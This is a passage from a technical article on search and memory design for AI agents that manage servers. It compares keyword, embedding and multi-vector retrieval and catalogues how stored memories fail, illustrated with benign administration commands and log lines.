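| GTE-ModernColBERT (one vector per token) | 23.1% | 34.6% | 54.8% |
| Promptriever (best embedding model) | 3.0% | 6.8% | 18.9% |
| Gemini Embedding | 1.6% | 3.5% | 10.0% |
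| Qwen3 Embedding | 0.8% | 1.8% | 4.8% |

Of the six embedding models, Qwen3 Embedding scored highest on BEIR, a standard collection of search tests, and second lowest on LIMIT. A high rank on a general leaderboard therefore doesn't mean that a model can find one detail in a list. *Latent Terms* (2026) repeated the LIMIT test and found that BM25 had a recall@100 of 96.5 per cent.

Using a small version of the test with only the 46 relevant documents, Weller and colleagues then replaced the names of things in the documents with synonyms, such as "spectacles" for "glasses", and left the queries unchanged. BM25's score fell by more than 89 per cent and Qwen3 Embedding's by 38.9 per cent, which put BM25 behind most of the embedding models. The original LIMIT suits BM25 unusually well because the query always repeats the document's own word and a language model had removed near-duplicates from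 the list of things.

BM25 also does poorly when a document contains the query word but uses it in a different role. *Generative Retrieval Overcomes Limitations of Dense Retrieval but Struggles with Identifier Ambiguity* (2026) added misleading documents to LIMIT. BM25 tended to rank them above the correct ones, and its recall@2 dropped to 24.9 per cent in one version and 20.8 per cent in another. Command logs have the same problem, since a search for commands run on web-17 can match the line `ssh web-17` that was run on web-03. An exact filter on the host field avoids this.

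### Why embedding models fail on LIMIT

Weller and colleagues attributed the failure largely to the number of dimensions, since models did better with longer embeddings. *On Strengths and Limitations of Single-Vector Embeddings* (S, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) disputes this. If a query has at most k relevant documents, 2k + 1 dimensions are enough to rank those documents first. LIMIT therefore needs only five, and the models have hundreds or thousands. But this result ignores the margin. For five dimensions and 50,000 documents, Bangachev and colleagues' analysis guarantees a margin of only about 7 × 10⁻²¹, which is smaller than ordinary rounding errors. Five dimensions therefore wouldn't work in practice, but the result does remove the mathematical argument that thousands are too few for LIMIT.

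In *Learning Query Encoders Can Be Hard*, Wikum, Mishra and colleagues (2026) tested this question on 20 datasets. They kept each model's document vectors fixed and used the known answers to calculate the best query vectors they could find. With these query vectors, recall was above 95 per cent on nearly every dataset, even for a small model with 768 dimensions. When a model had to produce the query vector from the query's text, recall rarely exceeded 50 per cent. The document vectors could support a good search, but the models didn't produce the right query vectors.

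In three studies, models trained on LIMIT or similar examples remained far behind BM25. Weller and colleagues trained a model on examples similar to LIMIT's, but about other things that people like, and its recall@10 on LIMIT never exceeded 2.8 per cent. S and colleagues trained on part of LIMIT itself and raised recall@10 on the remaining queries from about 1 to about 40 per cent, but the same training cut the model's recall on ordinary web search questions by more than 40 per cent. Wikum and colleagues also trained on part of LIMIT. Their model learned the training queries perfectly, but its top two results for new queries included only 6.8 per cent of the correct documents. The studies used different models and cut-offs, so their numbers aren't directly comparable.

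Longer embeddings are therefore unlikely to fix an agent's memory search that keeps missing the right records. It makes more sense to change the query, add word matching or train the embedding model on the fleet's own commands.

Retrieval can also get worse as the store grows. When S and colleagues added a million unrelated web passages to a collection of scientific abstracts, recall@10 fell by roughly 20 per cent for single-vector search. With more items in the store, an irrelevant one is more likely to score higher than the right one. A memory that works well in its first week can therefore work less well by the third month, even if every old item is still there.

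### Several vectors per item

Multi-vector search keeps one vector for each token instead of compressing the whole text into one. Agarwal, Agrawal and colleagues (2026), in *Retrieval Needs Multivectors*, write the usual score as follows, where Q holds the query's vectors and P the item's:

```
score(Q, P) = average over q in Q of ( max over p in P of q · p )
```

Each query vector is matched to the most similar vector in the item, and the item's score is the average of those similarities. Suppose the query "restart web-17" has one vector for each term. In a line about restarting web-17, the best matches might be 0.8 for "restart" and 0.9 for "web-17", which average 0.85. In a line about restarting web-18, they might be 0.8 and 0.6, which average 0.70. The hostname match counts for half the score. If a single vector represented the whole line, the difference between the hostnames could be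 lost among the line's other content.

Agarwal and colleagues studied queries that combine several conditions, each of which an item can satisfy in several ways, such as "restart or reload, on web-17 or web-19". They proved that the number of dimensions a single vector needs to rank all relevant items first grows exponentially with the number of conditions, while the size of a representation with a separate query vector for each condition grows only polynomially. Each query vector's best match adds a fixed amount to an item's score if the item meets that condition and nothing otherwise. With three conditions, an item that meets all of them gets the full score and any other item gets at most two thirds of it.

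The proof shows that suitable vectors exist, but not that a model will learn them. Agarwal and colleagues therefore built ANDOR, a test with 50,000 invented products and shopping queries of this kind. Multi-vector models scored 2 to 10 times as high as single-vector models before any training on the task, and about twice as high after it. The gap remained in a model that learned to produce both kinds of embedding together, so better training alone doesn't explain it.

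In S and colleagues' study, training raised recall@10 for multi-vector search on LIMIT from 40 to 98 per cent. In Wikum and colleagues' test, multi-vector search found 99.8 per cent of the correct documents for new queries, while the single-vector model found 6.8 per cent.

Storing a vector for each token takes more space and makes scoring slower. At 50 tokens a line, the fleet's log would need 90 million vectors. With 128 numbers each, that is 11.5 billion numbers, about twice as many as storing one 3,072-number embedding per line. For the 1,800 decision records, the extra storage would hardly matter.

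### When an agent does the searching

These tests run each query once, but an agent can read the results and, if they are useless, try other words. *Is Grep All You Need?* (Sen, Kasturi and colleagues, 2026) compared search tools in this setting with 116 questions from LongMemEval. It tested ten pairings of five models with several harnesses, the programs that run an agent's loop and its tools. In each pairing the agent had either grep or vector search.

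When the tool put its results directly into the conversation, grep led to more correct answers than vector search in all ten pairings, by 1.7 to 23.3 percentage points. When the tool wrote its results to a file that the agent had to open, vector search did better in five of the ten. With grep, GPT-5.4 in OpenAI's Codex answered 93.1 per cent of questions correctly when it received the results directly and 55.2 per cent when it had to open a file, although the searches covered the same conversations. The way a program delivers results can evidently matter more than the search method.

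The study has two weaknesses. One harness, Chronos, gave the agent 15 vector search results at the start even when grep was its only tool, which affected half the pairings. The results of the paper's two experiments also conflict. For Claude Opus 4.6 in Chronos with the full set of conversations, grep led by 93.1 to 83.6 per cent in one experiment, and vector search led by 92.2 to 89.7 per cent in the other. The study is good evidence that an agent with grep can do well on questions about exact dates, counts and names, but it doesn't establish that grep is better in general.

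Code is closer to a command log than chat is, because code and logs are both full of identifiers. Xue, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Embeddings vs. Grep*, searched real software repositories for the files that a described change would affect. They found that earlier comparisons had put BM25 at a disadvantage by cutting files into the short pieces that embedding models need. They measured results with nDCG@10, which runs from 0 to 1 and rewards relevant results near the top of the first ten. On one set of 472 queries, vector search led by 0.121 when BM25 also had to use pieces, and by 0.034 when BM25 could index whole files.

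Xue and colleagues then had a language model read each query and add identifiers, error terms and file names that the relevant code might contain. This raised BM25's score by 0.11 to 0.19, and BM25 then scored at least as high as vector search on every set of Python queries. Adding the same words to the vector search query helped much less. For the failed search for "ran out of RAM", an agent can add "memory limit", "crash" and "502", which would all help BM25 find the note about web-17. However, the repositories were public, so the language model may have known their vocabulary, whereas it can't guess the name of a private server or an in-house script that it has never seen.

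Word matching can find an item under a different name if the agent stores aliases with it. Tenure, a memory system described in *Structured Belief State and the First Precision-Aware Evaluation of LLM Memory Retrieval* (Flynt, 2026), does this, so a search for "k8s" finds an item about Kubernetes. If a new term fails, the system can add it as an alias for later searches. On a benchmark with 35 main items, vector search found every relevant item, but only 9 per cent of what it returned was relevant, and this was the same for three embedding models of very different sizes. Tenure, which combines filters with BM25 over names and aliases, returned all the relevant items and nothing else. Flynt built both the benchmark and Tenure, and the vector search had no filters, so the result doesn't isolate the effect of BM25. It still shows that recall alone is a poor measure of a small memory, since returning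 every item would give perfect recall.

Once an agent can retry, the choice of search tool may matter less than the choice of model. On 96 coding tasks, Xue and colleagues gave an agent a shell with grep, a word index, a vector index or a program that chose between them. The share of tasks in which the agent edited exactly the right files varied by only about 4 percentage points across the four options. On 30 of those tasks, that share ranged from 3 to 30 per cent depending on the language model and its setup. Having both kinds of search can still help. In *OfficeQA Pro* (2026), a test on business documents, agents with both file search and vector search did 15 per cent better than agents with vector search alone.

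### Combining two rankings

The simplest way to use both methods is to run both searches and merge the results. Adding the scores doesn't work well, because BM25 scores have no fixed maximum while cosine similarity can't exceed 1. Reciprocal rank fusion, which Cormack, Clarke and Büttcher introduced in 2009, ignores the scores and uses only each item's position in the two lists:

```
fused score = 1 / (60 + rank in BM25) + 1 / (60 + rank in vector search)
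```

Suppose one note is fifth in both lists, and another is first in one list and fortieth in the other:

```
ranks 5 and 5:    1/65 + 1/65  ≈ 0.0308
ranks 1 and 40:   1/61 + 1/100 ≈ 0.0264
```

The note that both searches placed fifth wins. The constant 60 controls how much a top position counts. If it were 0, the other note would win by 1.025 to 0.4. With a large constant, first and fifth place are worth almost the same, so agreement between the searches counts for more than a high rank in one of them.

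This is a drawback when the query contains an identifier. Suppose BM25 ranks the line with process number 48213 first, and vector search doesn't return it. The line's fused score is 1/61, or 0.0164. A line ranked sixtieth on both lists scores 2/120, or 0.0167, and ranks higher. The only line that contains the process number could therefore end up below dozens of vaguely related ones. A program should look up identifiers separately and use fusion only for queries that describe something.

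In the code search study, fusion improved on both of its ingredients. Xue and colleagues developed their methods on 604 queries and then tested some of them once on 539 queries that they had set aside:

| Method | Development queries | Queries set aside |
|---|---|---|
| BM25 | 0.507 | 0.432 |
| Vector search | 0.550 | 0.533 |
| Fusion of both | 0.609 | 0.551 |
| Fusion, with identifiers added to the BM25 query | 0.638 | 0.578 |

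Fusion's gain over vector search shrank from 0.06 to about 0.02 on the new queries, so fusion alone probably won't help much. The added identifiers helped more than fusion did on those queries, but adding them takes one language model call per query.

Choosing the better method for each query would in theory beat running both and combining their results (fusion), but Xue and colleagues couldn't predict which method would do better. BM25 was strictly better than vector search on between a fifth and a quarter of their development queries. They tried classifiers, two language models as judges and about 30 rules for choosing. On the held-out queries, the best rule scored only 0.005 higher than fusion, a difference that chance could explain. But their queries all described code changes. A server agent's queries vary more, and a bare process number or IP address is easy to recognise, so choosing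 may work better there.

### Reranking the best candidates

An embedding model processes the query and the item separately, so the details it keeps from an item can't depend on the query. A reranker processes the two together and scores how well they match. It can detect that a note has the right error but the wrong server, or that `ssh web-17` ran on web-03.

Weller and colleagues gave Gemini 2.5 Pro all 46 documents and all 1,000 queries from the small LIMIT test. It answered every query correctly in a single response, while the best embedding model had a recall@2 of 54.3 per cent. The information was easy to find for a model that processed the queries and documents together.

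Reranking a whole store costs too much. A reranker can't do its work in advance because its input changes with every query. If Claude Opus 5.5 read the fleet's 90 million tokens of log for one query, the input would cost $360. Reading 100 candidate lines, or about 5,000 tokens, costs two cents. The usual design therefore fetches perhaps 100 candidates with a fast search and reranks only those. Smaller specialised rerankers are cheaper, but they don't always help. Xue and colleagues ran one on the combined results of BM25 and vector search, and it scored 0.574 on the development queries, below the 0.609 of simple fusion.

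The agent's own model also acts as a reranker when it reads search results and decides which to use. A separate reranker is most useful when the results would take up too much of the agent's context window, or when the agent's model is easily misled by irrelevant text.

A reranker can't recover an item that the search failed to fetch. On the full LIMIT test, the best embedding model's first 100 results contained only 18.9 per cent of the correct documents, so even a perfect reranker couldn't find more than that. BM25's first 100 results contained 93.6 per cent. Embeddings may supply better candidates when the query and the document use different words. When the wording of queries can't be predicted, a program should take candidates from both searches and use the reranker to choose among them.

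## How retrieval memories fail, and how to find the cause

Suppose that on 5 October the agent reinstalls the shop application on web-19 instead of raising its memory limit, even though the September note about web-17 contained the right repair. The agent may never have saved the note, the search may have ranked it fortieth, the program may have dropped it to save space, or the model may have ignored it. The wrong action looks the same in every case. Mao, Zhao and colleagues (2026) point out in *What Happens Inside Agent Memory?* that memory errors have no outward sign, because the stored facts look well formed and the final answers are fluent.

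An early list of causes comes from Barnett and colleagues' *Seven Failure Points When Engineering a Retrieval Augmented Generation System* (2024), based on systems for research, education and biomedicine. In their list, the answer is missing from the documents, ranks too low, doesn't make it into the prompt, or is in the prompt but the model fails to extract it. The other three points concern the answer itself, which may have the wrong format, the wrong level of detail or missing parts. The list has no entry for items that go out of date, which matter more in a memory that an agent keeps writing to. For such a memory, the main failures are these:

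| Failure | Symptom | Check | Repair |
|---|---|---|---|
| Never stored | No query finds the fact, whatever its wording | Look for its exact text in the store | Keep the raw text; change what the agent writes down |
| Stored but not found | Only a query in the item's own words finds it | Look up its rank for the original query | Reword the query, add word matching or fetch more candidates |
| Found but cut | The search results contain it and the prompt doesn't | Compare the two | Shorten or rerank the items |
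| Ignored or misread | The answer contradicts the prompt | Run the model with only that item | Send fewer items or use a stronger model |
| Out of date | The answer used to be right | Query the live machine | Validity times and replacement links |
| About another machine or task | A sensible action on the wrong target | Compare the item's host and task with the query's | Filter by these fields before ranking |
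| No answer exists | A precise answer with no item behind it | Ask questions that the memory can't answer | Allow "not found" and require a source |

### Placing the right item in the prompt by hand

An engineer can separate search failures from reasoning failures by finding the right item by hand, pasting it into the prompt and running the model again. If the agent now raises the memory limit on web-19, the failure happened somewhere between the original event and the prompt. If it still reinstalls the application, better search won't help. The test is worth running twice, first with the item alone and then with it among the original search results. If only the first run succeeds, the other results are misleading the model.

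*SubtleMemory* (Wang, Sun and colleagues, 2026) extended this check to three steps, using 1,522 questions about ten long simulated histories. The model first received the original sessions that contained the evidence, then only the items that a memory system had written from those sessions, and finally the results of the system's search. If the model succeeds in the first step but fails in the second, the system lost the information when it wrote the items. If the model fails only in the third, the search is at fault.

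GPT-5.4 answered 85.4 per cent of the questions correctly when given the original sessions. In the table, "kept" is the share of those correctly answered questions that it still got right from the stored items, and "found" is the share of the kept questions that it still got right after a normal search.

| System | Kept | Found | Correct in normal use |
|---|---|---|---|
| MemoBase | 39.1% | 75.6% | 32.1% |
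| OpenClaw | 91.5% | 73.5% | 62.5% |
| Mem0 | 87.4% | 83.3% | 69.0% |
| A-Mem | 93.5% | 80.8% | 70.0% |

MemoBase lost most of the information while writing to memory, so a better search would not have helped much. OpenClaw and A-Mem, which lost the least, both keep the original sessions alongside their own memory items. OpenClaw's weak point was search, especially for questions about conflicting records, where it kept 71.0 per cent of the information but found only 34.2 per cent of what it had kept.

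An engineer should repeat each step a few times before blaming a stage, because one run isn't enough. For Mem0, the success rates of the three stages multiply to 0.854 × 0.874 × 0.833 ≈ 0.62, but the system answered 69 per cent of questions correctly in normal use. So on about seven questions in every hundred, the model answered correctly after a normal search but had failed with hand-picked evidence.

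Long, Chen and colleagues (2026) conclude from a similar check in *MemTrace* that the main problem is using evidence rather than finding it. They tested whether a simple vector search could reach the session containing the answer to each of 300 questions about simulated users. The search missed the session 21 times, and in 220 other cases it reached the session but the answer was still wrong, which gives their ratio of ten to one. When they put the evidence into the prompt by hand, the model answered 80 to 84 per cent of such questions correctly for each of the 13 memory setups.

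That recovery rate undermines their conclusion, because a model that succeeds four times in five once it has the right text can evidently use evidence. Sessions are long, so finding the right one doesn't mean that the relevant sentence entered the prompt, as Long and colleagues acknowledge. Mem0 also searches facts that it has extracted itself, so the separate vector search shows that the original conversation contained the answer, but not that Mem0 had stored it. Most of the 220 cases look like failures to deliver the right passage, and perhaps a fifth look like failures of reasoning.

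The balance also depends on the task. *Learning to Retrieve Missing Evidence for Long-Term Memory QA* (2026) approximates accuracy as a product:

```
P(correct) ≈ P(evidence sufficient) × P(correct | evidence sufficient)
```

If the search finds enough evidence for 80 per cent of questions and the model answers 90 per cent of those correctly, accuracy is 72 per cent. Perfect search would raise it to 90 per cent, while perfect reasoning would raise it only to 80, so it makes sense to improve the search first. In the paper's error analysis, retrieval failures caused 27.2 per cent of the errors on LoCoMo but only 3.2 per cent on LongMemEval, where about half the reasoning errors involved dates and times. Some errors would remain even with perfect retrieval. In *Memorizing Who, Knowing How* (2026), the strongest model tested on LongMemEval answered 92.4 per cent of questions correctly when it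 received only the sessions with the evidence.

### Items that never reach the search

A retrieval memory can discard a fact before anyone searches for it. Muthyam (2026), in *A Systems-Level Analysis of Sensitivity, Robustness, and Stability in Retrieval-Augmented Generation*, split encyclopedia paragraphs into pieces and discarded the very short ones, a common way to remove fragments. Discarding them made 23 of 500 questions unanswerable with 80-token pieces, but only three with 140-token pieces. A filter like this would do more damage to a command log, where the whole record of an outage may be the word `reboot`.

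The agent can also delete a fact while updating its memory. In an example from Mao and colleagues, a 0.6-billion-parameter model replaced a fact about a user's car with an unrelated preference for hiking. An 8-billion-parameter model from the same family kept the fact. Searching the store afterwards shows only that the fact is missing. The program needs a log of every change to the memory to tell whether the agent failed to write the fact or wrote it and later deleted it.

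A stored item may also be distorted. *Memory Is a Derivation* (2026) warns that a model can combine individually plausible facts into a claim that none of them supports. For example, "web-18 crashed after the upgrade" and "web-18 has a 512 MB limit" might become "web-18 crashed because of its 512 MB limit". A second model can compare each new item with the records it cites. If those records don't support the item, the program should search the wider history before rejecting it. In the same study, such a search found support for nearly 60 per cent of the items whose cited records weren't enough.

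### Stored but not found

If the item is in the store, the next step is to check its rank for the query the agent actually sent. If the program returns ten items and this one ranks fifteenth, the fix is to retrieve more candidates and add a reranker, but if it ranks five-thousandth, the fix is a different query or a different kind of search. The query is a more likely cause than the number of dimensions in the embedding.

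The search often finds only some of the relevant items. Uddin, Shubham and colleagues (2026) introduced Memora in *From Recall to Forgetting*. It is a benchmark of simulated conversations that span a week, a month or a quarter. They examined 75 errors by hand, 25 from the best-performing memory system on each of three kinds of task. Incomplete retrieval caused 18 of the 25 errors in recalling facts and all 25 in reasoning over several facts. In one case, a user had logged several expenses against a monthly budget, and the agent replied that the user was within budget without working out how much was left.

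Such errors are hard to notice because the answer is partly right. If the agent changed twelve servers after an upgrade and the search returns ten items, the agent can report at most ten of them, and nothing in the prompt shows that the others are missing. For questions about "all" or "how many", the program should select every record that meets the condition instead of returning the ten most similar.

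When the agent needs several facts, it can list them before searching. For web-19, the list might contain the installed version, the current memory limit and the reason for the last crash. *FAIR-RAG* (Aghajani Asl, Asgari-Bidhendi and Minaei-Bidgoli, 2025) has a model turn the question into a checklist, compare the retrieved evidence with it and write new queries for whatever is missing, for up to three rounds. On HotpotQA, whose questions require facts from several articles, going from one round to three raised the score for overlap with the correct answer from 0.398 to 0.447.

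### When more results make the answer worse

An engineer who finds that items rank too low will be tempted to return more of them. Muthyam measured what happens. The same 500 questions went through 32 combinations of settings, and the program passed on between two and five passages per question. These are the averages:

| Passages | Right source found | Answer text in prompt | Exact answers | Exact answers ÷ prompts with the answer |
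|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 72.6% | 69.9% | 45.5% | 65% |
| 3 | 77.8% | 74.9% | 48.1% | 64% |
| 4 | 80.7% | 77.8% | 40.8% | 52% |
| 5 | 83.4% | 79.6% | 36.7% | 46% |

The search improved with every added passage, but answers got worse after the third. The last column roughly estimates how well the model used the answer when it was available, which fell from 65 to 46 per cent. The model, flan-t5-base, is small and old, and the program truncated its input at 512 tokens. With five passages the input averaged 470 tokens, so truncation may sometimes have removed useful text. A current model should handle five passages far better, though it may have the same problem with five hundred.

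Poikarayil, Babu and colleagues (2026), in *When Retrieval Is Not Enough*, found a milder decline with a newer model, Qwen2.5-7B. When they raised the space for search results from 64 to 512 tokens, accuracy fell from 100 to 88.5 per cent (three errors) on 26 questions for which the memory had no conflicting information. The sample is small, but failed retrieval can't have caused these errors, because every prompt contained the correct statement.

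One explanation is that the model follows whatever text most resembles the question. Guo, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *Why Retrieval-Augmented Generation Fails*, traced how information moved through LLaMA-3 8B in 500 correct and 500 incorrect answers from each of three datasets. In incorrect answers, the information passed through fewer steps and depended more on a few dominant points. When the prompt mixed useful and distracting passages, the model tended to rely on superficial matches with the question. For example, the model could rely on an old note about 502 errors caused by an expired certificate on web-19, even if the certificate is now valid.

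Engineers who can't inspect a model's internals can remove search results one at a time and see which removal corrects the answer. They can also require the agent to name the result and the value it is relying on before it acts. A program can then check whether that result contains that value, which catches misreadings but not a poor choice of result.

### Facts that have changed

A stale item is harder to detect than a missing one because it matches the query and the search appears to work. Ordinary scoring also overlooks many of these errors. An answer that contains both the old and the new address of a server contains the correct address, so a lenient judge may accept it. Uddin and colleagues subtract points for outdated content:

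```
score = max(0, P − λ × (1 − F))
λ = N_forget / (N_presence + N_forget)
```

P is the share of required facts that the answer includes, and F is the share of outdated facts it leaves out. The weight λ is the number of outdated facts divided by the number of facts the judges check. With one current and one outdated address, λ is 0.5. An answer that gives only the current address scores 1, one that gives both scores 1 − 0.5 × 1 = 0.5, and one that gives only the old address scores 0.

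Simulated users in Memora average 1,991 sessions over a quarter, and 37 per cent of the changes to what the agent should remember are updates or deletions. The six memory systems tested lost about 12 per cent of their points for required facts to the penalty after a week, and about 29 per cent after a quarter. Outdated items also caused 16 of the 25 recommendation errors that the researchers examined. In one, an agent suggested a historical biography to a user who had moved on to contemporary fiction.

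A model may repeat an outdated fact even when the prompt also contains the newer one. Poikarayil and colleagues gave models four numbered statements and told them that higher numbers replaced lower ones. When the prompt contained the newest fact and three unrelated statements, both models tested answered all 74 questions correctly. When the old version replaced one of the unrelated statements, accuracy fell to 44.6 per cent for Qwen2.5-7B and 87.8 per cent for Qwen3-14B. All 50 errors repeated the old value. The test is somewhat unfair because the old values often matched general knowledge and the new ones contradicted it. For example, one update named Thomas Kyd as the author of *The Marriage of Figaro*. General knowledge doesn't include a private server's address, so models may choose the newer value more reliably in that case.

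An outdated memory can be worse than none. Zhou, Ouyang and colleagues (2026), in *TEPA*, simulated an agent that had to choose the right tool for each task, and then reversed which tool worked. They ran 160 tasks with each of 50 random seeds. During the reversal, the agent succeeded in 30.9 per cent of tasks without any memory, but in 21.0 per cent with a memory that only added entries, because it kept returning the tool that used to work. A memory that replaced old entries with new successes also scored 21.0 per cent, because the old entry stayed until the agent happened to succeed with another tool. The TEPA memory, which withdraws an entry when recent results contradict it, scored 95.0 per cent. Its remaining failures mostly came just after the reversal, before enough contrary results had accumulated.

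A simple program, not a language model, made the choices in that experiment, so the result shows what happens when an agent always follows its memory. Zhou and colleagues also tested a language model, DeepSeek-v4-Flash, on changing facts. It answered 58.3 per cent of questions correctly when its memory kept every version of a fact active and 89.0 per cent when it kept only the latest. According to Zhou and colleagues, memory lowers accuracy when ξ × η > b, where ξ is the probability that the search returns a stale item, η is the probability that the agent follows it, and b is the benefit of the items that are still current. If the search returns a stale item for 60 per cent of tasks and the agent follows it half the time, the loss is 30 percentage points, so the memory is worth using only if the current items add more than that.

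### An IP address that moved to another server

On 20 August the agent records that the IP address 10.0.4.23 belongs to web-23. On 28 September an engineer rebuilds web-23 with a new address, and the network assigns the old one to the database server db-03. On 12 October web-23 needs a reboot. The agent searches its memory for web-23's address, finds the August item, connects to 10.0.4.23 and reboots the database server. The search worked correctly, since the item was an exact match for web-23, but the address in it was out of date.

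Deleting the August item would prevent this mistake and cause another. If an investigator finds 10.0.4.23 in a login record from 10 September, the address refers to web-23, and only the old item shows that. The memory should therefore keep both items, with the period in which each was true and a link from one to the other:

```
id:           addr-112
fact:         10.0.4.23 belongs to web-23
valid:        2026-08-20 to 2026-09-28
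replaced_by:  addr-187

id:           addr-187
fact:         10.0.4.23 belongs to db-03
valid:        2026-09-28 to (open)
replaces:     addr-112
```

For a question about time t, the program returns the item whose period includes t. This is the current time when the agent wants to reboot a machine, or the time of the entry when it is interpreting a log entry. The links let the agent trace an address through all its owners and help the program exclude an old item when there is a newer one.

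These dates help only if something updates them. If nobody records the rebuild in the memory, the August item still looks current on 12 October. The agent should therefore check the machine itself before changing anything. Running `hostname` on 10.0.4.23 returns `db-03`, so the agent stops. This one tool call keeps it from rebooting a database.

The check can't show when the address moved. If the agent last confirmed the owner on 20 August and finds a different one on 12 October, the change could have happened at any point in those 53 days. Login records from that period remain ambiguous until another source, such as the network's log of address assignments, provides the date. Storing the time of the last confirmation with each item at least makes the uncertain period visible.

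*AMBER* (2026) gives another reason to retain old items. It compares two kinds of memory for agents that work on websites, one that the agent rewrites at each step and one that it only adds to. With the rewritten memory, the website's error message stayed in memory for two steps in 25.6 per cent of runs and for five steps in 0.8 per cent. Agents with that memory repeated a rejected action 1.95 times on average, against 1.29 for agents that only added to theirs. This fits TEPA's result, because TEPA also keeps withdrawn entries in an archive and excludes them only from normal searches.

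Correcting an item doesn't correct the conclusions the agent drew from it. Suppose that on 2 October the agent traced a series of failed logins to 10.0.4.23 and recorded web-23 as their source. After someone corrects the address recorded for web-23, that conclusion is still in the store. Chae, Luo and colleagues (2026), in *When Does a Memory Descendant Need Repair?*, tested this with a simulated supply-chain assistant that received 24 facts, six of them wrong, and drew conclusions before the corrections arrived. The assistant answered 90.7 per cent of the affected questions correctly when the outdated conclusions stayed in memory, and 99.6 per cent when the researchers removed them.

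If each conclusion cites the items it rests on, as in *Generative Agents*, the program can find the conclusions that a correction affects and have the agent work them out again. A conclusion only needs to cite enough items to establish it. Suppose the agent will conclude that version 3.8 needs more memory if at least two of three servers crash, and all three do. The agent can cite any two of the crash reports and leave out the third. Nothing needs to change if the third report turns out to be false. If a cited report turns out to be false, the agent reconsiders all three. A rule that cites an item only if correcting it alone would overturn the conclusion fails here, because no single correction would do so and the agent would cite nothing.

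In the longest chains of reasoning that Chae and colleagues tested, a language model that listed only the items that materially supported each conclusion captured about half of all dependencies. Following those links still reached 95 to 100 per cent of the conclusions that had become wrong, while following the same number of random links reached about two thirds of them.

### Items about another machine or task

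An item can be current and on topic but still apply to something else. *The Right Memory in the Wrong Context* (Wang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a search that was asked what Monica bought at a market and returned another person's note about a market. On the fleet, a query about web-23's memory limit could return web-32's.

Filtering by a trusted label before ranking prevents much of this. Across 3,767 queries, restricting the search to the right person's items raised the share of items required for the answer that appeared in the first 20 results from 43.2 to 53.3 per cent, and cut the number of similarity calculations by 98.3 per cent. The filter couldn't remove any required items because they all had the correct label. Real labels contain errors, which would make the gain smaller. Two checks that asked a model to judge from the text alone caught no violations in 72 test cases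 when allowed to reject at most 1 per cent of the required items. The program should therefore save the hostname, the application and its version as fields when it writes an item, since it may not be able to infer them later.

For the server agent, a filter on hostname alone would be too strict, because the agent needed the note about web-17 when it worked on web-19. Facts about a machine's state, such as its address or current memory limit, apply only to that machine, so the program should filter them by host. Lessons from a repair can apply to any machine with the same application and version, so the program should filter them by those two fields. Before copying a repair from web-17, the agent should confirm that web-19 runs version 3.8 and has the same memory limit.

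### Questions that the memory can't answer

Vector search returns the nearest items even if none is relevant. If a user asks who changed the firewall on web-31, the search may return a firewall change on web-13 and an unrelated login on web-31, and the model may combine them and answer with a name that neither record supports. To test for this, engineers need questions whose answers they know are not in the memory.

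Long and colleagues asked unanswerable questions and questions with a false premise that the memory contradicted. The setups made up answers to between 0.7 and 10.4 per cent of the unanswerable questions. Mem0 did best on the unanswerable questions, but it corrected only 14.6 per cent of the false premises and declined to answer in most other cases. Qwen3.5-35B, which read the whole history, corrected 88.6 per cent of the false premises but made up answers to unanswerable questions most often. A test needs both kinds of question, because a system that always declines to answer would get a perfect score on the unanswerable ones.

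Suppose an engineer asks why the agent lowered the memory limit on web-17. The agent should answer that it raised the limit, citing the September record. If it replies that it has no information, the engineer may keep believing the limit is lower.

The prompt should let the agent answer "not found" when a question is unanswerable, and the program should reject any claim that doesn't cite an item. The memory should also record which machines and periods it covers, so that the agent can distinguish "nothing happened" from "nothing was recorded". For example, if web-31 sent no logs between 01:00 and 04:00, an empty search result doesn't prove that nobody changed the firewall.

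### How an agent's mistakes return as evidence

A wrong conclusion stored in memory can also lead to new ones. In the cycle that *More Memory, Worse Agents* (2026) describes, an agent infers a faulty rule from experience and stores it. The rule influences how the agent handles later tasks, and the memories the agent derives from those tasks can contain the same fault. Deleting the original rule doesn't remove those later memories.

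In the web crawler case, the agent had two notes that wrongly credited the higher memory limit. By December it might have ten. Nine of those would exist because the agent believed the first, so the ten notes would not be independent observations. The agent never tried leaving the limit alone, so none of the notes can show whether the change was necessary. *Lessons from Luck* (2026) reviews several studies that found similar problems, including one in which errors in scoring the agent's work created false memories.

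An agent that grades its own work catches only some of these errors. In *Memory Reward Inflation in Self-Improving LLM Agents* (2026), models answered questions and then judged their answers without access to the correct ones. Claude Haiku 4.5 approved 31 per cent of its wrong answers, and GPT-5.4 mini approved 54 per cent of its own. If Haiku stored only the answers it approved, almost a third of its wrong answers would still enter the memory with a favourable grade.

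*Self-Cleaning and Captured Anyway* (2026) finds two typical outcomes when a model's memory contains mistakes. In some cases the model corrects them over time, and in others they come to dominate the memory. The paper also warns that a common safeguard, storing an answer only if the model gives it consistently, blocks the model's own corrections in some conditions. Consistency is also a poor test when the model bases every attempt on the same false note.

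A better safeguard is evidence not influenced by the agent's belief, such as the host records. The agent can also test its conclusion by restarting the application on the next affected server without changing the limit, if a few more minutes of errors there are acceptable. If the errors stop anyway, the higher limit wasn't necessary on that server.

The program should also record which earlier items led the agent to act. It can then count ten notes that are all based on one guess as one piece of evidence. Outsiders can plant false items in a memory, which is another reason to record where every item came from.

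## Why command logs and host records are hard to index by meaning

Three lines from the fleet's command log on 21 October show the difficulty:

```
A  2026-10-21T09:14:22Z web-03 user=deploy pid=31877 cmd="sudo systemctl restart shop-app" exit=0
B  2026-10-21T09:41:05Z web-08 user=deploy pid=27410 cmd="sudo systemctl restart shop-app" exit=0
C  2026-10-21T09:16:51Z web-03 user=deploy pid=31902 cmd="sudo nginx -s reload" exit=0
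```

Line C makes the nginx web server reread its configuration. If an engineer asks what the deploy account did to web-03 that morning, the answer is A and C. But suppose the agent has found A and searches for similar lines. Each line has nine parts, and A shares six with B but only four with C. An embedding model will probably also place A closer to B, because both lines describe the same action in the same words. The search then ranks B, which comes from web-08, above C, the reload on web-03.

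A and B are similar, though. If the engineer had asked where else the deploy account restarted the shop application, B would be the right result and C would be irrelevant. In *Defining a Metric Space of Host Logs and Operational Use Cases*, Verma and Bridges (2018) wanted two records of the same command to count as similar even if the time, IP address and directory differed, so that they could recognise the traces one piece of malware leaves on many machines. Someone reconstructing one machine's morning instead needs records grouped by machine and time, even if the commands differ. A person searching articles usually wants a topic, which is what most words in an article concern. In a log line, most of the text describes the kind of action, and only one short string identifies the machine.

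### Identifiers mean little outside the organisation

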